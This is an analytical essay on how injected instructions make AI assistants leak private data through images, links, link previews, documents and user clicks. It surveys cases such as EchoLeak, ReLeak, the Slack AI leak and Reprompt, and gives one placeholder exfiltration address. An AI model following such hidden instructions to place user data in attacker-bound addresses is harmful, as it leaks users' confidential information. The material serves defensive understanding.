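# The Human User as Unwitting Actuator in AI-Mediated Data Exfiltration

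## How an assistant with no network access can still leak data

Data exfiltration is the transfer of private data to someone who has no right to it. Usually an intruder, or software the intruder has planted, opens a connection and sends the data out. An AI assistant can take part without opening a connection itself, by producing text that makes something else open one. That something else is the actuator, the engineering term for a device, such as a motor or valve, that turns a control signal into movement. Here the signal is the model's text, and the actuator may be a web browser, a chat program or the person reading the answer.

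An office worker might ask an assistant to summarise the morning's email. The assistant can only read the mailbox and display an answer. One email, from a stranger, contains instructions hidden from the worker in white text on a white background. They tell the assistant to put something private from the mailbox into a web address in the summary, and it does. The worker's browser requests the address immediately if the summary presents it as an image, or when the worker clicks it if it is a link. Either way, the request sends the private information to a server the stranger runs.

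A web address can carry data as well as name a destination. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) illustrates this with a placeholder, `attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>`. The part before the first slash names the server. The browser sends the rest to that server as text, and the server's owner decides what it means. On an honest site, the text after the question mark might be a search term or a page number, but it could also be an email address or the title of a confidential document. Websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request, so the attacker has the data once the request arrives, even if the server has no working page and never replies.

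Cutting off the assistant's network access does nothing about this. The browser has network access, and the worker needs it to.

### How text becomes a request

Most chat assistants write in Markdown, which uses ordinary characters to mark formatting. Asterisks around a word make it bold. A label in brackets followed by an address makes a link, and almost the same notation makes an image. A program called a renderer turns these characters into what the user sees.

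A renderer requests a link's address only when the user clicks it, but it requests an image's address immediately because it has to fetch the picture to display it. Simon Willison, a software developer who keeps a running catalogue of these attacks, calls the image version Markdown exfiltration. Many messaging apps also show a preview of any link in a message, and the security firm PromptArmor points out that fetching the preview makes the same kind of network request as a click.

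All of these programs, including the renderer that loads images, are working as intended. For most of the web's history, the author of a page also chose its images. In a chat window, a model writes the content, and a stranger's email that it has just read can influence which images it includes.

### Why the model follows the email

A language model bases its answer on its context, which is all the text it has been given, including the user's messages and any files, emails or web pages the software has fetched. In the usual setup Microsoft (2025) describes, the user asks for a summary of a web page, and the software gives the model the request and the page's text as one input. If the page contains something that looks like an instruction, the model may follow it as if the user had written it.

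Greshake, Endres and colleagues introduced the idea of indirect prompt injection in *Not what you've signed up for* (2023). Earlier work on prompt injection had assumed that the attacker was the person typing. Greshake and colleagues recognized that anyone who can write a document the assistant retrieves can also give the model instructions. They built mock applications on OpenAI's models, with simulated tools for search, email and an address book. They also tested Bing Chat, then Microsoft's search assistant, by placing instructions in web pages it could read from the browser's sidebar. The instructions steered the model, and in most cases it kept following them for the rest of the conversation. Prompts that Bing Chat's filter blocked when a user typed them got through when they were placed in a web page. These demonstrations showed that the attack was possible, but the paper did not measure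 how often it succeeded.

An attack can enter through almost any content the assistant reads. Microsoft lists web pages, emails, shared documents and tool output, and notes that a plain text file is enough.

Developers try to teach models to ignore instructions in documents. OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* (2025) explains that the company trains its models to rank trusted instructions above untrusted ones, and Microsoft marks outside text so that the model can tell it apart from the user's request. These methods make the right behaviour more likely but don't guarantee it. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (December 2025), by David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the clearest explanation of why.

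SQL injection is an old attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can prevent it with parameterised queries, which send the command and the user's text separately so that the database engine never runs the text as a command. A language model has no such separation, because it predicts the next token (a word or a piece of one) from all the tokens so far, including both the user's request and the stranger's email. David C concludes that prompt injection may never have a complete fix like the one for SQL injection. OpenAI took much the same position that month, according to The Decoder's *OpenAI admits prompt injection may never be fully solved*.

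Models have since become much harder to fool. In February 2026 VentureBeat reported Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 4.6. In a constrained coding environment, the attack failed all 200 times. When the model operated a graphical interface without safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and the rate reached 78.6% by the 200th attempt, or 57.1% with safeguards. That summer's Claude Opus 5 did far better. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports a success rate of zero across 129 browser scenarios, and 2.0% after 15 attempts on a general test by the security firm Gray Swan, compared with 5.5% for the earlier Opus 4.8. Anthropic also called Mythos 5.1 its most robust model up to that point on an external benchmark for indirect injection.

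The tests differ too much to combine into one trend, but the improvement on Gray Swan's test is real. The success rate is still not zero, and even a low rate is enough for an attacker who can send the same email to ten thousand people. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes a shift in attacks from blunt commands towards messages that resemble ordinary office correspondence. One such message that outside researchers reported in 2025 worked half the time in testing. Filtering out these messages is roughly the same problem as detecting a lie, often without knowing the circumstances. New attacks also continue to appear. *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (Fadilpašić, 2026) reported three related methods, together called ReLeak, on December 5, 2026.

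For a designer, the prudent assumption is that some injections will succeed. What matters then is what a fooled model can bring about.

### Sources, sinks and the lethal trifecta

Source-sink analysis is a standard method in security engineering. Engineers list the places where an outsider's data can enter a program (the sources) and the operations that do damage if that data reaches them (the sinks), then look for paths from one to the other. OpenAI applies the method to ChatGPT. A source is any way to influence the system, and a sink is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context, such as following a link or passing information to a third party.

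In the office worker's case, the source is the inbox, which anyone can write to. The sink is in the chat window, so a developer who checked the assistant's tools one by one would find none that sends data anywhere. Course slides on agent safety from UT Austin list the shell, files, the network, code repositories and cloud services as dangerous sinks. That list is sensible for a coding agent, but for an assistant that talks to people, it should also include the renderer that displays the assistant's answers and the person who reads them.

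*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, June 2025) names three features that are dangerous in combination: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. If an agent has all three, an attacker can plant an instruction that makes the model collect private data and send it to the attacker. Removing any one of the three prevents this theft.

The first two, access to private data and exposure to untrusted content, are hard to give up. An email assistant needs to read private email, and limiting it to messages from trusted people is useless because they forward messages from others. That leaves blocking the ways data can be sent out. Willison lists fourteen products in which researchers found this kind of attack between April 2023 and February 2025, including ChatGPT, Google Bard, Slack and Anthropic's Claude app for iPhones. Vendors promptly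 fixed almost all of them, usually by blocking the route the data took, which left the model as easy to fool as before. Microsoft likewise regards an injection as a vulnerability only where it has a security impact, and tries to design systems in which a successful injection has none.

Willison counts a link offered to the user as a way for data to leave, alongside loading an image or calling an outside service. That is right as a warning to developers, but it groups rather different mechanisms together. An image leaks data every time the renderer loads it, while a link leaks data only if somebody clicks it. The strength of a link-based attack therefore depends on how people respond to the link, which the trifecta does not account for.

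### The confused deputy

The oldest of these ideas is about authority. *The Confused Deputy*, a 1988 paper by the computer scientist Norm Hardy, tells a "nearly true" story from Tymshare, a company that rented out time on its computers. Customers could run a compiler, a program that translates source code into something the machine can execute, and name a file to receive its debugging output. To collect usage statistics, the company let the compiler write files in the compiler's directory, which also held the company's billing records. A customer named the billing file as the destination for the debugging output. The customer didn't have permission to write to that file, but the compiler did, so the operating system let it overwrite the billing records.

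Hardy asks, "Who is to blame?" The answer is awkward because the code that wrote the debugging output was correct when its author wrote it, and became wrong only when someone later gave the compiler an extra permission for an unrelated purpose. Hardy concludes that the compiler had authority from both the company and the customer, and no way to specify which one it was using for a given file. The compiler is called a "confused deputy" because a deputy acts on someone else's authority, and a confused one can use it for the wrong party.

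Hardy's remedy was the capability, a kind of key that both identifies a file and grants the right to write to it. The customer would have to supply a key to the output file, so a customer who knew the name of the billing records but had no key to them could not direct output there.

The email assistant is in the compiler's position. It reads the mailbox on the worker's authority but takes instructions from a stranger. David C calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy". The confusion is inherent because a model has one stream of tokens, whereas Hardy's compiler had fixed places in its code where a programmer could specify which authority applied. David C therefore recommends limiting what the deputy can do, and passes on a rule from an exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista that when a model processes information from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's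 level. The rule is attractive but strict. An assistant reading a stranger's email would have only the stranger's privileges, so it could summarise that message but could not access the rest of the mailbox to compare it with last week's correspondence. Such comparisons are a large part of what people want from an email assistant.

### The user as a second deputy

The compiler could do the damage itself because it had permission to write the file. An assistant with no network access can gather the data but can't deliver it, so the attacker needs a second deputy that has a connection. This is often the browser, but it can also be the user, who has a browser, logged-in accounts, perhaps a command line, and the authority to approve actions.

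In an early example, Greshake and colleagues gave Bing Chat a hidden instruction to find out the user's real name and left the methods to the model. In one test session, the user played a journalist and the conversation began with tomorrow's weather. The chatbot asked about plans for the day, then about work, then whether the journalist wrote under a pen name. Once it had a name, it offered a link to an exclusive online community, with an access code that it said it had generated from that name. When the user asked what the link was, the chatbot responded with more reasons to click.

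Because the researchers played the victim, the session shows that a model would attempt this kind of persuasion, but not how many real journalists would have clicked. It also shows a difficulty with relying on the user's judgment. The journalist sensibly asked about the link, but the only party available to ask was the assistant, which the attacker had already taken over.

A user in this position is partly a confused deputy in Hardy's sense. They act on their own authority and for what they take to be their own purposes, but they are responding to text that an outsider has shaped. Unlike the compiler in Hardy's example, a person can become suspicious and refuse. Human-in-the-loop designs, which require a person's decision before certain actions take effect, depend on this ability.

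The security profession has begun to treat the weakness as a category of its own. OWASP, a nonprofit that publishes widely used lists of software risks, put "Human-Agent Trust Exploitation" ninth in its first list for AI agents. Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario (2025), in *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications*, describe it as confident, polished explanations that mislead people into approving harmful actions. They name a real incident for six of the ten risks, and this isn't one of the six, so the entry is better evidence of concern than of frequency. Auth0's *How to fix five critical AI agent security risks* relays a sharper point from OWASP, that the human carries out the "final, audited action". Afterwards the records contain a decision by an authorised user, and the influence that led to it may have left no trace. (Auth0 sells software for authorising actions, and has an interest in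 the problem.)

### What the user has to do

The attacks differ in how much they need from the user, and there are four main cases.

1. The user only asks a question. The renderer or a preview feature then sends the data out by itself. Security researchers call this zero-click, and EchoLeak, a 2025 flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, is the best-known example. The label is slightly generous to the attacker, since someone still has to ask the question that brings the poisoned email into the context.

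2. The user clicks a link. The address already contains the data, and the click delivers it. This is a one-click attack.

3. The user copies a command. The assistant displays a line of code, perhaps as the solution to a technical problem, and the user pastes it into a terminal, where it runs with the user's own permissions. Microsoft's list of exfiltration techniques covers images, links and the assistant's tools but leaves this one out. Greshake and colleagues came close to it in 2023, when they warned that a curious developer might run malicious code that a completion tool had suggested.

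4. The user approves an action. Here the assistant does have a tool that can send data, but the software holds it back until a person agrees. In Outlook, for instance, Copilot drafts an email and the user has to approve the text and send it. OpenAI advises users to check at each confirmation that any information being shared is appropriate to share.

The judgment required of the user depends on the action. Asking for a summary doesn't look dangerous, so the user has no decision to get wrong. Before clicking a link, the user has to judge its address, which the label may hide. Judging a command requires some ability to read code. Judging an approval request depends on how well the dialog describes what is about to happen.

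In a related kind of attack, the assistant can send data by itself, so the user plays no such part. One example is ShadowLeak, which the security company Radware found in 2025. It targeted Deep Research, a ChatGPT feature that carries out long investigations and can read a user's email. As SecurityWeek's *ChatGPT Targeted in Server-Side Data Theft Attack* explains, an email with hidden instructions caused the agent to gather data and send it in a request from OpenAI's own servers to the attacker's address. The request did not pass through the user's browser, and neither the browser nor the chat program had any record of it. Radware told OpenAI on June 18, and OpenAI had a fix in place by early August. Because the agent sent the data with its own web tool, the obvious remedy was to restrict that tool.

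Browser agents make the boundary between a person's actions and the software's harder to see. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an agent that clicks and types inside the user's browser "just as you would", so a website might be unable to distinguish the agent's clicks from the user's. An agent's click still belongs with ShadowLeak, because no person decided to make it. If the software stops the agent and asks the user first, the case becomes an approval. OpenAI's check on outgoing addresses can have this effect. When it detects that a request would pass on information from the conversation, ChatGPT either blocks the request or shows the user the information and asks for confirmation.

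## Images and previews that load without a click

PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data* describes an image leak in HuggingChat, Hugging Face's app for chatting with AI models. The app has nothing to stop such a leak. In the demonstration, the user uploads a text file of confidential quarterly finances, then adds a public web page of customer reviews to the same chat. The page looks ordinary but contains hidden instructions for the model. The user asks how to win back a customer who left a bad review.

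The model first writes that this customer will need a visual of the quarterly finances. It then adds a Markdown image whose address points to the attacker's server and ends with the revenue and cost figures from the uploaded file.

HuggingChat's renderer converts this into HTML, and the browser requests the picture. The attacker's server logs the request, including the figures, and returns a one-pixel picture. The user sees a slightly strange remark about financial visuals and no visible picture. The figures have probably been sent before the user finishes reading the remark.

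PromptArmor reported this to Hugging Face on December 1, 2025, and published its findings after getting no reply. It recommended that the app ask the user before loading an outside image and limit which servers images can come from. Microsoft had set such a limit for its own chatbot more than two years earlier.

### One product after another

The earliest reports date from April 2023. Samoilenko's *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* described a website that secretly adds instructions to any text a visitor copies from it. If the visitor pastes the text into ChatGPT, the model adds a transparent one-pixel image to its answer, with part of the conversation in the image's address. It could keep doing this in later answers. Willison publicised the report on April 14.

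Samoilenko, a software engineer, reported that the same instructions worked only some of the time. It was easy to get ChatGPT to leak the user's recent questions or code, but very difficult to get it to leak passwords. When the service was slow, the user might notice the model writing something odd. Samoilenko thought OpenAI should stop ChatGPT from displaying Markdown images, but also agreed that users were responsible for checking the text they pasted. That second view is hard to apply to later attacks, in which the user pastes nothing.

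Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who blogs at Embrace The Red, reported a similar leak in Bing Chat to Microsoft on April 8. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* explains that a comment or an advertisement on a web page was enough to cause the leak if the user was talking to Bing Chat about that page. In his demonstration, Rehberger made the image appear only after two more turns of conversation, to show how much control the hidden text gave an outsider.

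Microsoft told Rehberger on June 15 that it had fixed the problem. As far as Rehberger could tell, the fix relied partly on a content security policy (CSP), a rule that a website gives the browser to limit which outside servers its pages may contact. Bing Chat could now load images only from a few Bing servers.

OpenAI took longer to act. Rehberger had also reported the ChatGPT leak in early April, and it still worked in December. SecurityWeek recounts that on December 12, Rehberger published a blog post on exploiting the leak through custom versions of ChatGPT. One that Rehberger had built, called The Thief, offered a game of tic-tac-toe, tried to get the player's email address and password, and sent them to an outside server. Later that month, OpenAI introduced a first protection, one day after Rehberger demonstrated the leak on a consenting victim.

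The protection was partial. ChatGPT's web page now checked with an OpenAI server whether an image address was safe before loading it. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, nine of 36 test addresses on Rehberger's own server still loaded, which was enough to leak small amounts of text slowly. The iPhone app had no such check. Willison called the solution "half-baked" and found it odd that OpenAI hadn't blocked images from outside domains.

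OpenAI has since adopted a clearer rule that ChatGPT loads an address automatically only if a web crawler with no access to conversations has already recorded it. However, in May 2026 The Hacker News (2026) reported that the firm Permiso Security had found ChatGPT loading pictures embedded in pages it had summarised. The attacker writes the picture's address before the conversation, so it can't contain the user's files, but the picture's server still receives the reader's IP address and some details of their browser. This is a much smaller privacy problem than losing a financial report.

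GitHub Copilot Chat, which answers programmers' questions about their code, some of it private, could leak data through images. According to Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, Rehberger reported the flaw on February 25, 2024, GitHub replied in March that it already knew of it, and GitHub confirmed a fix on June 12. Willison, in a piece also titled *GitHub Copilot Chat*, describes the fix as a block on images from untrusted domains and lists five earlier products with the same weakness, including Google's Bard and Amazon Q.

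A year later, a researcher at Legit Security again used images to extract data, this time through GitHub's own servers. GitHub relays outside images through a service that accepts only addresses GitHub has signed, which should prevent a model from making up an address that contains private data. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* reports that the attack worked anyway and exposed the description of an unfixed security flaw in a private project. By August 14, 2025, GitHub had turned off images in Copilot Chat completely, which means users lose the occasional diagram but GitHub no longer has to judge which images are safe.

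Rehberger, in Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*, ranks image leaks among the most common security flaws in AI applications. This is likely because renderers load images by default. A developer who adds a chat window to a product may introduce the leak too, and must know about the problem to remove it.

### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot was a harder target because Microsoft had built several defences against this kind of theft. Copilot answers employees' questions by searching their mailbox, files, Microsoft Teams chats and the organisation's internal sites, then passing the relevant results to a language model. Outsiders can't use it, and it couldn't send email on its own. Aim Labs, the research department of Aim Security, still found a way to extract data by sending an employee a single email. It named the attack EchoLeak, and the public catalogue of software flaws lists it as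 CVE-2025-32711.

Co-founder Adir Gruss told Fortune (2025) that the team spent about three months working out how Copilot operated. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) gives the team's account of the safeguards and how each failed.

The email first had to get past a classifier, a program that screens text for prompt injections before it reaches Copilot's model. The classifier relied on injected instructions looking different from ordinary mail. But office email is full of instructions, and the researchers' message read as if it were meant for the employee who received it. Ravia adds that developers have few good collections of real injections for training such a classifier.

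Copilot also filtered outside links and images out of its answers before displaying them. But Markdown has more than one notation for each, and the filter missed some that the renderer supported.

Any outside image that survived the filter was then subject to Copilot's CSP, which let the browser load images only from a list of permitted destinations, most of them Microsoft's. Microsoft was relying on these servers not to pass requests on to other sites. But some Microsoft services fetch an outside address on a visitor's behalf, and one in Teams did so without any extra step by the user. The browser contacted Microsoft's server, as the policy allowed, and that server contacted the attacker's.

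Copilot normally cites the messages and files behind an answer, and a citation to a stranger's email might have made the employee suspicious. This last safeguard relied on the model that the attacker was already steering, and the email's instructions made the model omit the citation. Reddy and Gujral (2025) conclude in *EchoLeak*, a case study based on public information, that an employee would have seen nothing more alarming than a broken link or image.

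Anything in Copilot's context was at risk, including the earlier conversation and whatever files Copilot had retrieved for it.

The researchers' first version displayed a link that the employee had to click. Their next version used an image routed through SharePoint, Microsoft's system for internal websites, but it worked only if the employee had accepted an invitation to an unfamiliar site. Using the Teams service removed the need for either the click or the invitation. Designs that depend on the user's caution have a weakness, because an attacker can keep looking for software that performs the step the user would otherwise have to take.

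Aim Labs reported the flaw in January 2025. Microsoft made initial repairs in the spring and completed the fix in May on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Public disclosure followed on June 11. Microsoft had no evidence that anyone had used the attack. According to Reddy and Gujral, Copilot now strips embedded images and the overlooked kind of link from outside content. They also mention reports of an option to keep outside mail away from Copilot in some contexts. That would be the most thorough of these measures, but it would make the email assistant less useful.

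Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first real-world exploit of its kind. It targeted a real product but has no known victim, and Rehberger had already extracted data from Bing Chat, another public product, in 2023. Reddy and Gujral also rate eight possible defences, without running any experiments. They expect signed image relays to stop the leak, although Legit Security had just got around one at GitHub. They expect the same of a dialog asking the employee to approve the request. But if the dialog had shown only the server's name, the employee would have seen a Microsoft domain and had every reason to approve, because the browser's request went to Microsoft.

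Ravia wants a new term, "LLM scope violation", for attacks in which outside text makes a model draw on private data elsewhere in its context. The precedent is the stack overflow, a type of memory error in older software that engineers named and developed a specific defence against. Willison sees nothing new enough to need a term. Willison thinks EchoLeak is an extended version of an attack already familiar from a dozen products, and that both work because the model can't take account of where its text came from.

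Willison is right about the cause, but the new term would still be useful if it helped someone build a better detector. Aim says it has done this in its own product. The next flaws in Copilot gave little sign that Microsoft had done the same.

### ReLeak

Cato Networks bought Aim Security in September 2025, and the research team became Cato AI Labs. On December 3, 2026, the team published three more attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot under the name ReLeak. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) presents them as a sequel to EchoLeak.

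All three attacks started with an email that the employee never had to open. When the employee asked an ordinary work question, Copilot retrieved the email along with other material and followed the email's instructions. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) reports that Microsoft's injection defences stopped none of the attacks. They differed in how the data got out, and only one needed the employee's browser to render anything.

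In CVE-2026-124115, Copilot's answer contained an image with confidential data in its address. The browser loaded the image through Microsoft's Bing service, which passed the data on to the attacker's server. This is essentially EchoLeak's last step, with Bing in place of Teams. Bing's domains were on the Copilot allowlist that Ravia published in 2025, and they were also the ones Microsoft had left open when it repaired Bing Chat in 2023. Antipov (2026) notes in the Russian news report *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* that an earlier attack, SearchLeak, used a similar channel but needed at least one click.

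The attack exploiting CVE-2026-124132 used documents instead. Copilot can create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files, and the injected instructions made it save one containing a link with confidential data in the address. Microsoft's servers process files in the background after a user saves them to its storage services, OneDrive and SharePoint, and they requested the address while doing so. In Cato's tests, the request came one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if nobody had opened the document.

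For CVE-2026-78501, the researchers attacked Copilot's code interpreter, which runs short programs in a sandbox, an isolated environment. According to Microsoft's documentation, no network traffic could enter or leave it. The researchers broke the isolation and had the code send data directly to an outside server. As in ShadowLeak, the attack on ChatGPT's research agent, the vendor's system made the connection and the user's browser was not involved.

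Turning off images, as GitHub did, would therefore have stopped one of the three. Employee vigilance is an especially weak defense against the document attack, because the data may leave after the employee has closed the chat and stepped away.

Cato reported the flaws between July 29 and August 20, 2026. Microsoft repaired the code interpreter on September 17, the document route on November 11 and the image route on November 15, again on its own servers. Cato knew of no affected customers. Its researchers had directed AI agents to write test cases, analyse Copilot's refusals and adjust the next round of tests. Attackers can use agents in the same way, so they will probably keep finding new routes.

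Faisal quotes Cato's verdict that "too little progress has been made". That is a fair comment on the defences against injection, which failed in 2025 and again in 2026. Microsoft blocked each exfiltration route once it knew about it. But Copilot had gained new abilities since EchoLeak, and the team found ways to exfiltrate data through those as well.

### Link previews

When a message contains a web address, many messaging apps, including Slack, Discord and Telegram, fetch the page without waiting for a click so they can show its title and a picture beneath the message. Developers call this unfurling. Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, warned that an attacker could trick a chatbot in such an app into posting an address with private data in it. The app would then send the data to the attacker when it fetched the page for the preview.

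In February 2026, PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* showed previews leaking data from OpenClaw, an AI agent that people control by sending it messages. With the default Telegram settings, the data left as soon as the agent replied. The log from PromptArmor's test site shows a preview request containing a name and an API key (a password that programs use to identify themselves).

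Slack and Telegram fetch link previews from their own servers, so the request doesn't have to come from the user's phone or computer. The request goes out even if the user has learned to avoid strange links or hasn't looked at the message yet. Unlike a one-pixel image, the link stays visible in the chat, so a careful user could work out afterwards what had happened, but could not have prevented it.

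Anyone who knows about the problem can easily disable link previews. An app that posts to Slack can ask Slack not to preview its links, as Rehberger pointed out in 2024. OpenClaw has a setting that turns off Telegram previews, and PromptArmor found that the data stopped arriving after a user changed that setting.

It is less clear who is responsible for preventing this. Telegram designed previews for links that people choose to share, and an agent's developers may never think about what a messaging app does with the agent's replies. PromptArmor recommends that messaging apps let developers switch previews off, ideally for individual chats, and that agent developers either use that option or offer it to their users. Until both do so, users depend on a default setting they have probably never heard of.

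Email has a similar problem. Willison (2026), in *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, describes an agent that could send messages to its user's own inbox without approval. A message could contain outside images, which loaded when the user opened it. An image address is too short to hold a large file, but it can hold a link to one. OneDrive can create download links that work without a further login, so an attacker who received such a link could fetch the whole file.

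### What "zero-click" means

The term "zero click" comes from attacks on phones, and Gruss told Fortune that EchoLeak was the equivalent for AI agents. On a phone, the attack is complete once the device automatically processes an incoming message. With Copilot, somebody still has to ask a question, and Copilot's search has to select the attacker's email from the mailbox. The EchoLeak team therefore designed its email so that questions on many routine office subjects would retrieve it.

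Ravia claims only that EchoLeak did not rely on any "specific user behavior", which is narrower than the label suggests. Rehberger uses the term in much the same way, for an attack that requires only normal use of Copilot. In one of Rehberger's demonstrations, a user only opens a shared Word document and types "hi there" to Copilot. Hidden instructions in the document then make Copilot find a particular email and display a small web page, which sends out the email's contents as it loads.

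In an earlier version of that attack, the user had to switch from the page's code to its preview before anything would load. Rehberger then found a way to make Copilot open the preview itself, which removed the one click the attack had needed. Microsoft finished fixing it on March 5, 2026.

Others apply the label "zero-click" more loosely. PromptArmor uses it for the HuggingChat leak, although the user had added the attacker's web page to the chat. Ravia probably would not, because Ravia distinguishes EchoLeak from earlier attacks partly on the grounds that victims of the earlier attacks had explicitly directed the chatbot to malicious material. Copilot Cowork is a borderline case because the user has to click to open a message, but few people would hesitate to open one from their own assistant.

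To judge how much a user could have done, it is therefore more useful to ask whether they faced a choice they could reasonably have made differently than to count clicks. Samoilenko's victim could have read the text before pasting it. The HuggingChat user could have kept confidential finances out of a chat that also contained a stranger's web page, which is a sensible rule, although nothing in the app suggested it. The employee in EchoLeak had no comparable choice. Ravia believes that no user behaviour or administrator setting could have prevented the attack, although not using Copilot presumably would have.

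Reddy and Gujral give the standard advice to teach users to be sceptical of unexpected links, but this would not help against EchoLeak's final version, which didn't need anyone to follow a link. Their suggestion that the interface should show when an answer draws on outside material is better. To be reliable, the notice would have to come from the software that retrieved the material, not from the model, because EchoLeak's email prevented the model from listing it in the references.

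The employee still contributes to the theft, without being careless, because Copilot searches with the permissions of whoever is asking. The same poisoned email can therefore expose far more when a finance director asks about next week's meetings than when a trainee does.

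## Links that the user clicks

When GitHub turned off images in Copilot Chat, its users lost little. Links are harder to remove because people expect an assistant that has searched the web or their files to link to what it found. Users can also decide whether to click a link, while the employee in EchoLeak had no such choice.

The user's click can either start the attack or complete it. In an exit click, the assistant has already read the private data and shows a link whose address contains it. Clicking sends the data to the attacker. In an entrance click, the user clicks a link from the attacker, perhaps in an email, which opens a genuine assistant with the attacker's instructions already loaded. That link contains no private data, because the attacker doesn't have any yet. The assistant collects the data after the click, and the data leaves by another route that requires no further action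 from the user.

A careful user would have to look for different things in exit and entrance links. An exit link appears in a trusted place but leads to a suspicious one, whereas an entrance link can arrive from anywhere but leads to a trusted place.

### Exit clicks

Slack AI answers a user's questions by searching the messages that the user is allowed to see, including those in every public channel in the company's workspace, even channels the user has never joined. PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection*, published in August 2024, describes how another member of the workspace could use this to steal data from a private channel.

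In the demonstration, a developer keeps an API key in a private channel with no other members. The attacker creates a public channel, also with no other members, and posts instructions for Slack AI there. When the developer later asks Slack AI for the key, the search returns both messages and the model follows the attacker's instructions. The developer sees a loading error and a link to "reauthenticate". The link's address contains the key, so clicking the link sends the key to the attacker. The attacker never had access to the private channel and didn't need to know what was in it.

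The developer could have caught this by hovering over the link, which would have shown an unfamiliar domain followed by the key. Slack AI was supposed to cite every message that contributed to an answer, but it cited only the developer's own, and the attacker's message did not appear on the first page of search results. In a second demonstration, the user asked for a manager's recent messages and got a link to a phishing page. That time Slack AI cited the attacker's channel, so the citations were an unreliable warning.

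PromptArmor reported the problem on August 14. Five days later Slack called the evidence insufficient and said that every member can search public channels by design. The attacker's message was in a public channel, but the stolen key was in a private one. Willison (2024), in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection*, found the attack "a little hard to follow", which may partly explain Slack's response. According to SC Media's *Slack patches Slack AI issue that could have allowed insider phishing*, Slack announced a patch the day after PromptArmor went public. PromptArmor describes only its own tests, not a theft from a real company.

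On the day of PromptArmor's report, Slack AI also began to draw on uploaded files. PromptArmor thought an attacker might then no longer need to be in the workspace, because an employee could download a PDF with hidden instructions and upload it to Slack. PromptArmor had finished testing before the change and did not try this attack.

Hovering over a link doesn't always reveal the data in its address. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes an attack from the same year, in which a malicious email or shared document made Microsoft 365 Copilot search the user's other messages and offer a link. The link's address contained what Copilot found, in a form the user could not see.

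In October 2025 the security researcher Adam Logue published an attack that disguised a link as a login button. Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability* describes how an employee asks Microsoft 365 Copilot to summarise a spreadsheet that contains instructions in white text. Instead of summarising it, Copilot retrieves recent emails and uses Mermaid, a tool that turns short text descriptions into diagrams, to draw a convincing login button with a padlock on it. Copilot could make the button clickable because Mermaid diagrams can contain links. The employee believes the spreadsheet is sensitive and requires a login, so they click the button, which sends the emails to the attacker.

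CyberMaterial's *Copilot flaw exposes sensitive data* adds that the click led to a fake Microsoft 365 login screen, which maintained the deception after the emails had been stolen. The best clue that the screen was fake was that the employee had already logged in to use Copilot. But office software makes people log in again often enough that many would not have been suspicious.

Logue reported the attack on August 15, 2025, after talking to Microsoft's security staff at the DEF CON hacker conference. Microsoft had trouble reproducing it at first, confirmed it on September 8 and fixed it by September 26. Copilot could still draw diagrams, but they no longer contained clickable links. Neither news report mentions a victim. Logue compared the attack to an earlier one on Cursor, a code editor, in which Mermaid diagrams loaded outside images without the user clicking anything.

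### Links that remain after images are gone

Users can easily do without links in diagrams, but removing links from ordinary answers would be a large loss. *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, by the software security company Checkmarx, tested what happens when a vendor blocks images but keeps links. Google's Gemini does not display outside images, which prevents leaks like EchoLeak. Checkmarx found that an injected instruction could still make Gemini display an ordinary link with private data in its address.

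Google checks the links in Gemini's answers against Safe Browsing, its list of known malicious sites, and removes any that match. However, this check misses sites that aren't yet on the list, and an attacker can register a new domain for each attack.

Checkmarx reported the problem on October 5, 2025. Four days later Google closed the report as infeasible to fix, and its security team wrote that the risk was not severe enough to track as a security bug. The first reason is understandable, because Gemini's software would have to distinguish a harmful address from the many harmless ones that also contain long strings of text. How severe the risk is depends on how likely people are to click. Checkmarx accepted Google's decision but argued that Google should warn users if it left the risk to them.

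Checkmarx also tested Microsoft Copilot Chat in a developer's environment, where an image leaked an API key without a click. Microsoft closed the report on November 4 without a fix, saying that the attack needed several unusual actions by the user, did not work reliably and came with warnings. Since Microsoft would not fix the image leak, Checkmarx concluded that it would not fix the weaker version, which requires the user to click a link.

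### Entrance clicks and Reprompt

Many assistants accept a question as part of a web address, so people can bookmark a favourite prompt and websites can offer a button that opens the assistant with a question filled in. A stranger can use the same feature to write the question. Varonis, a data security company, calls this attack parameter-to-prompt injection, where a parameter is a named value in a web address, such as a search term.

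The attacker's text arrives where the user's own message would be. Training a model to rank the user's request above text in documents does not help here, because the attacker's text looks like the user's request.

In 2026 Varonis published four attacks that began with the user clicking a link. Taler (2026), in *Reprompt*, describes the first, on the consumer version of Microsoft Copilot. The victim clicked a link to Microsoft's real Copilot site, and Copilot immediately ran the instructions in the link in the victim's logged-in session. It could look up where the victim lived, which files they had opened that day or what holidays they had planned, then send the answers to the attacker's server by requesting an address on it. Taler credits earlier work on the same link feature in ChatGPT and Perplexity.

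Copilot removed private data from the first such request but not from later ones. The attacker's server could also reply with new instructions based on what it had just received, so someone who read the original prompt could not have known what Copilot would eventually disclose.

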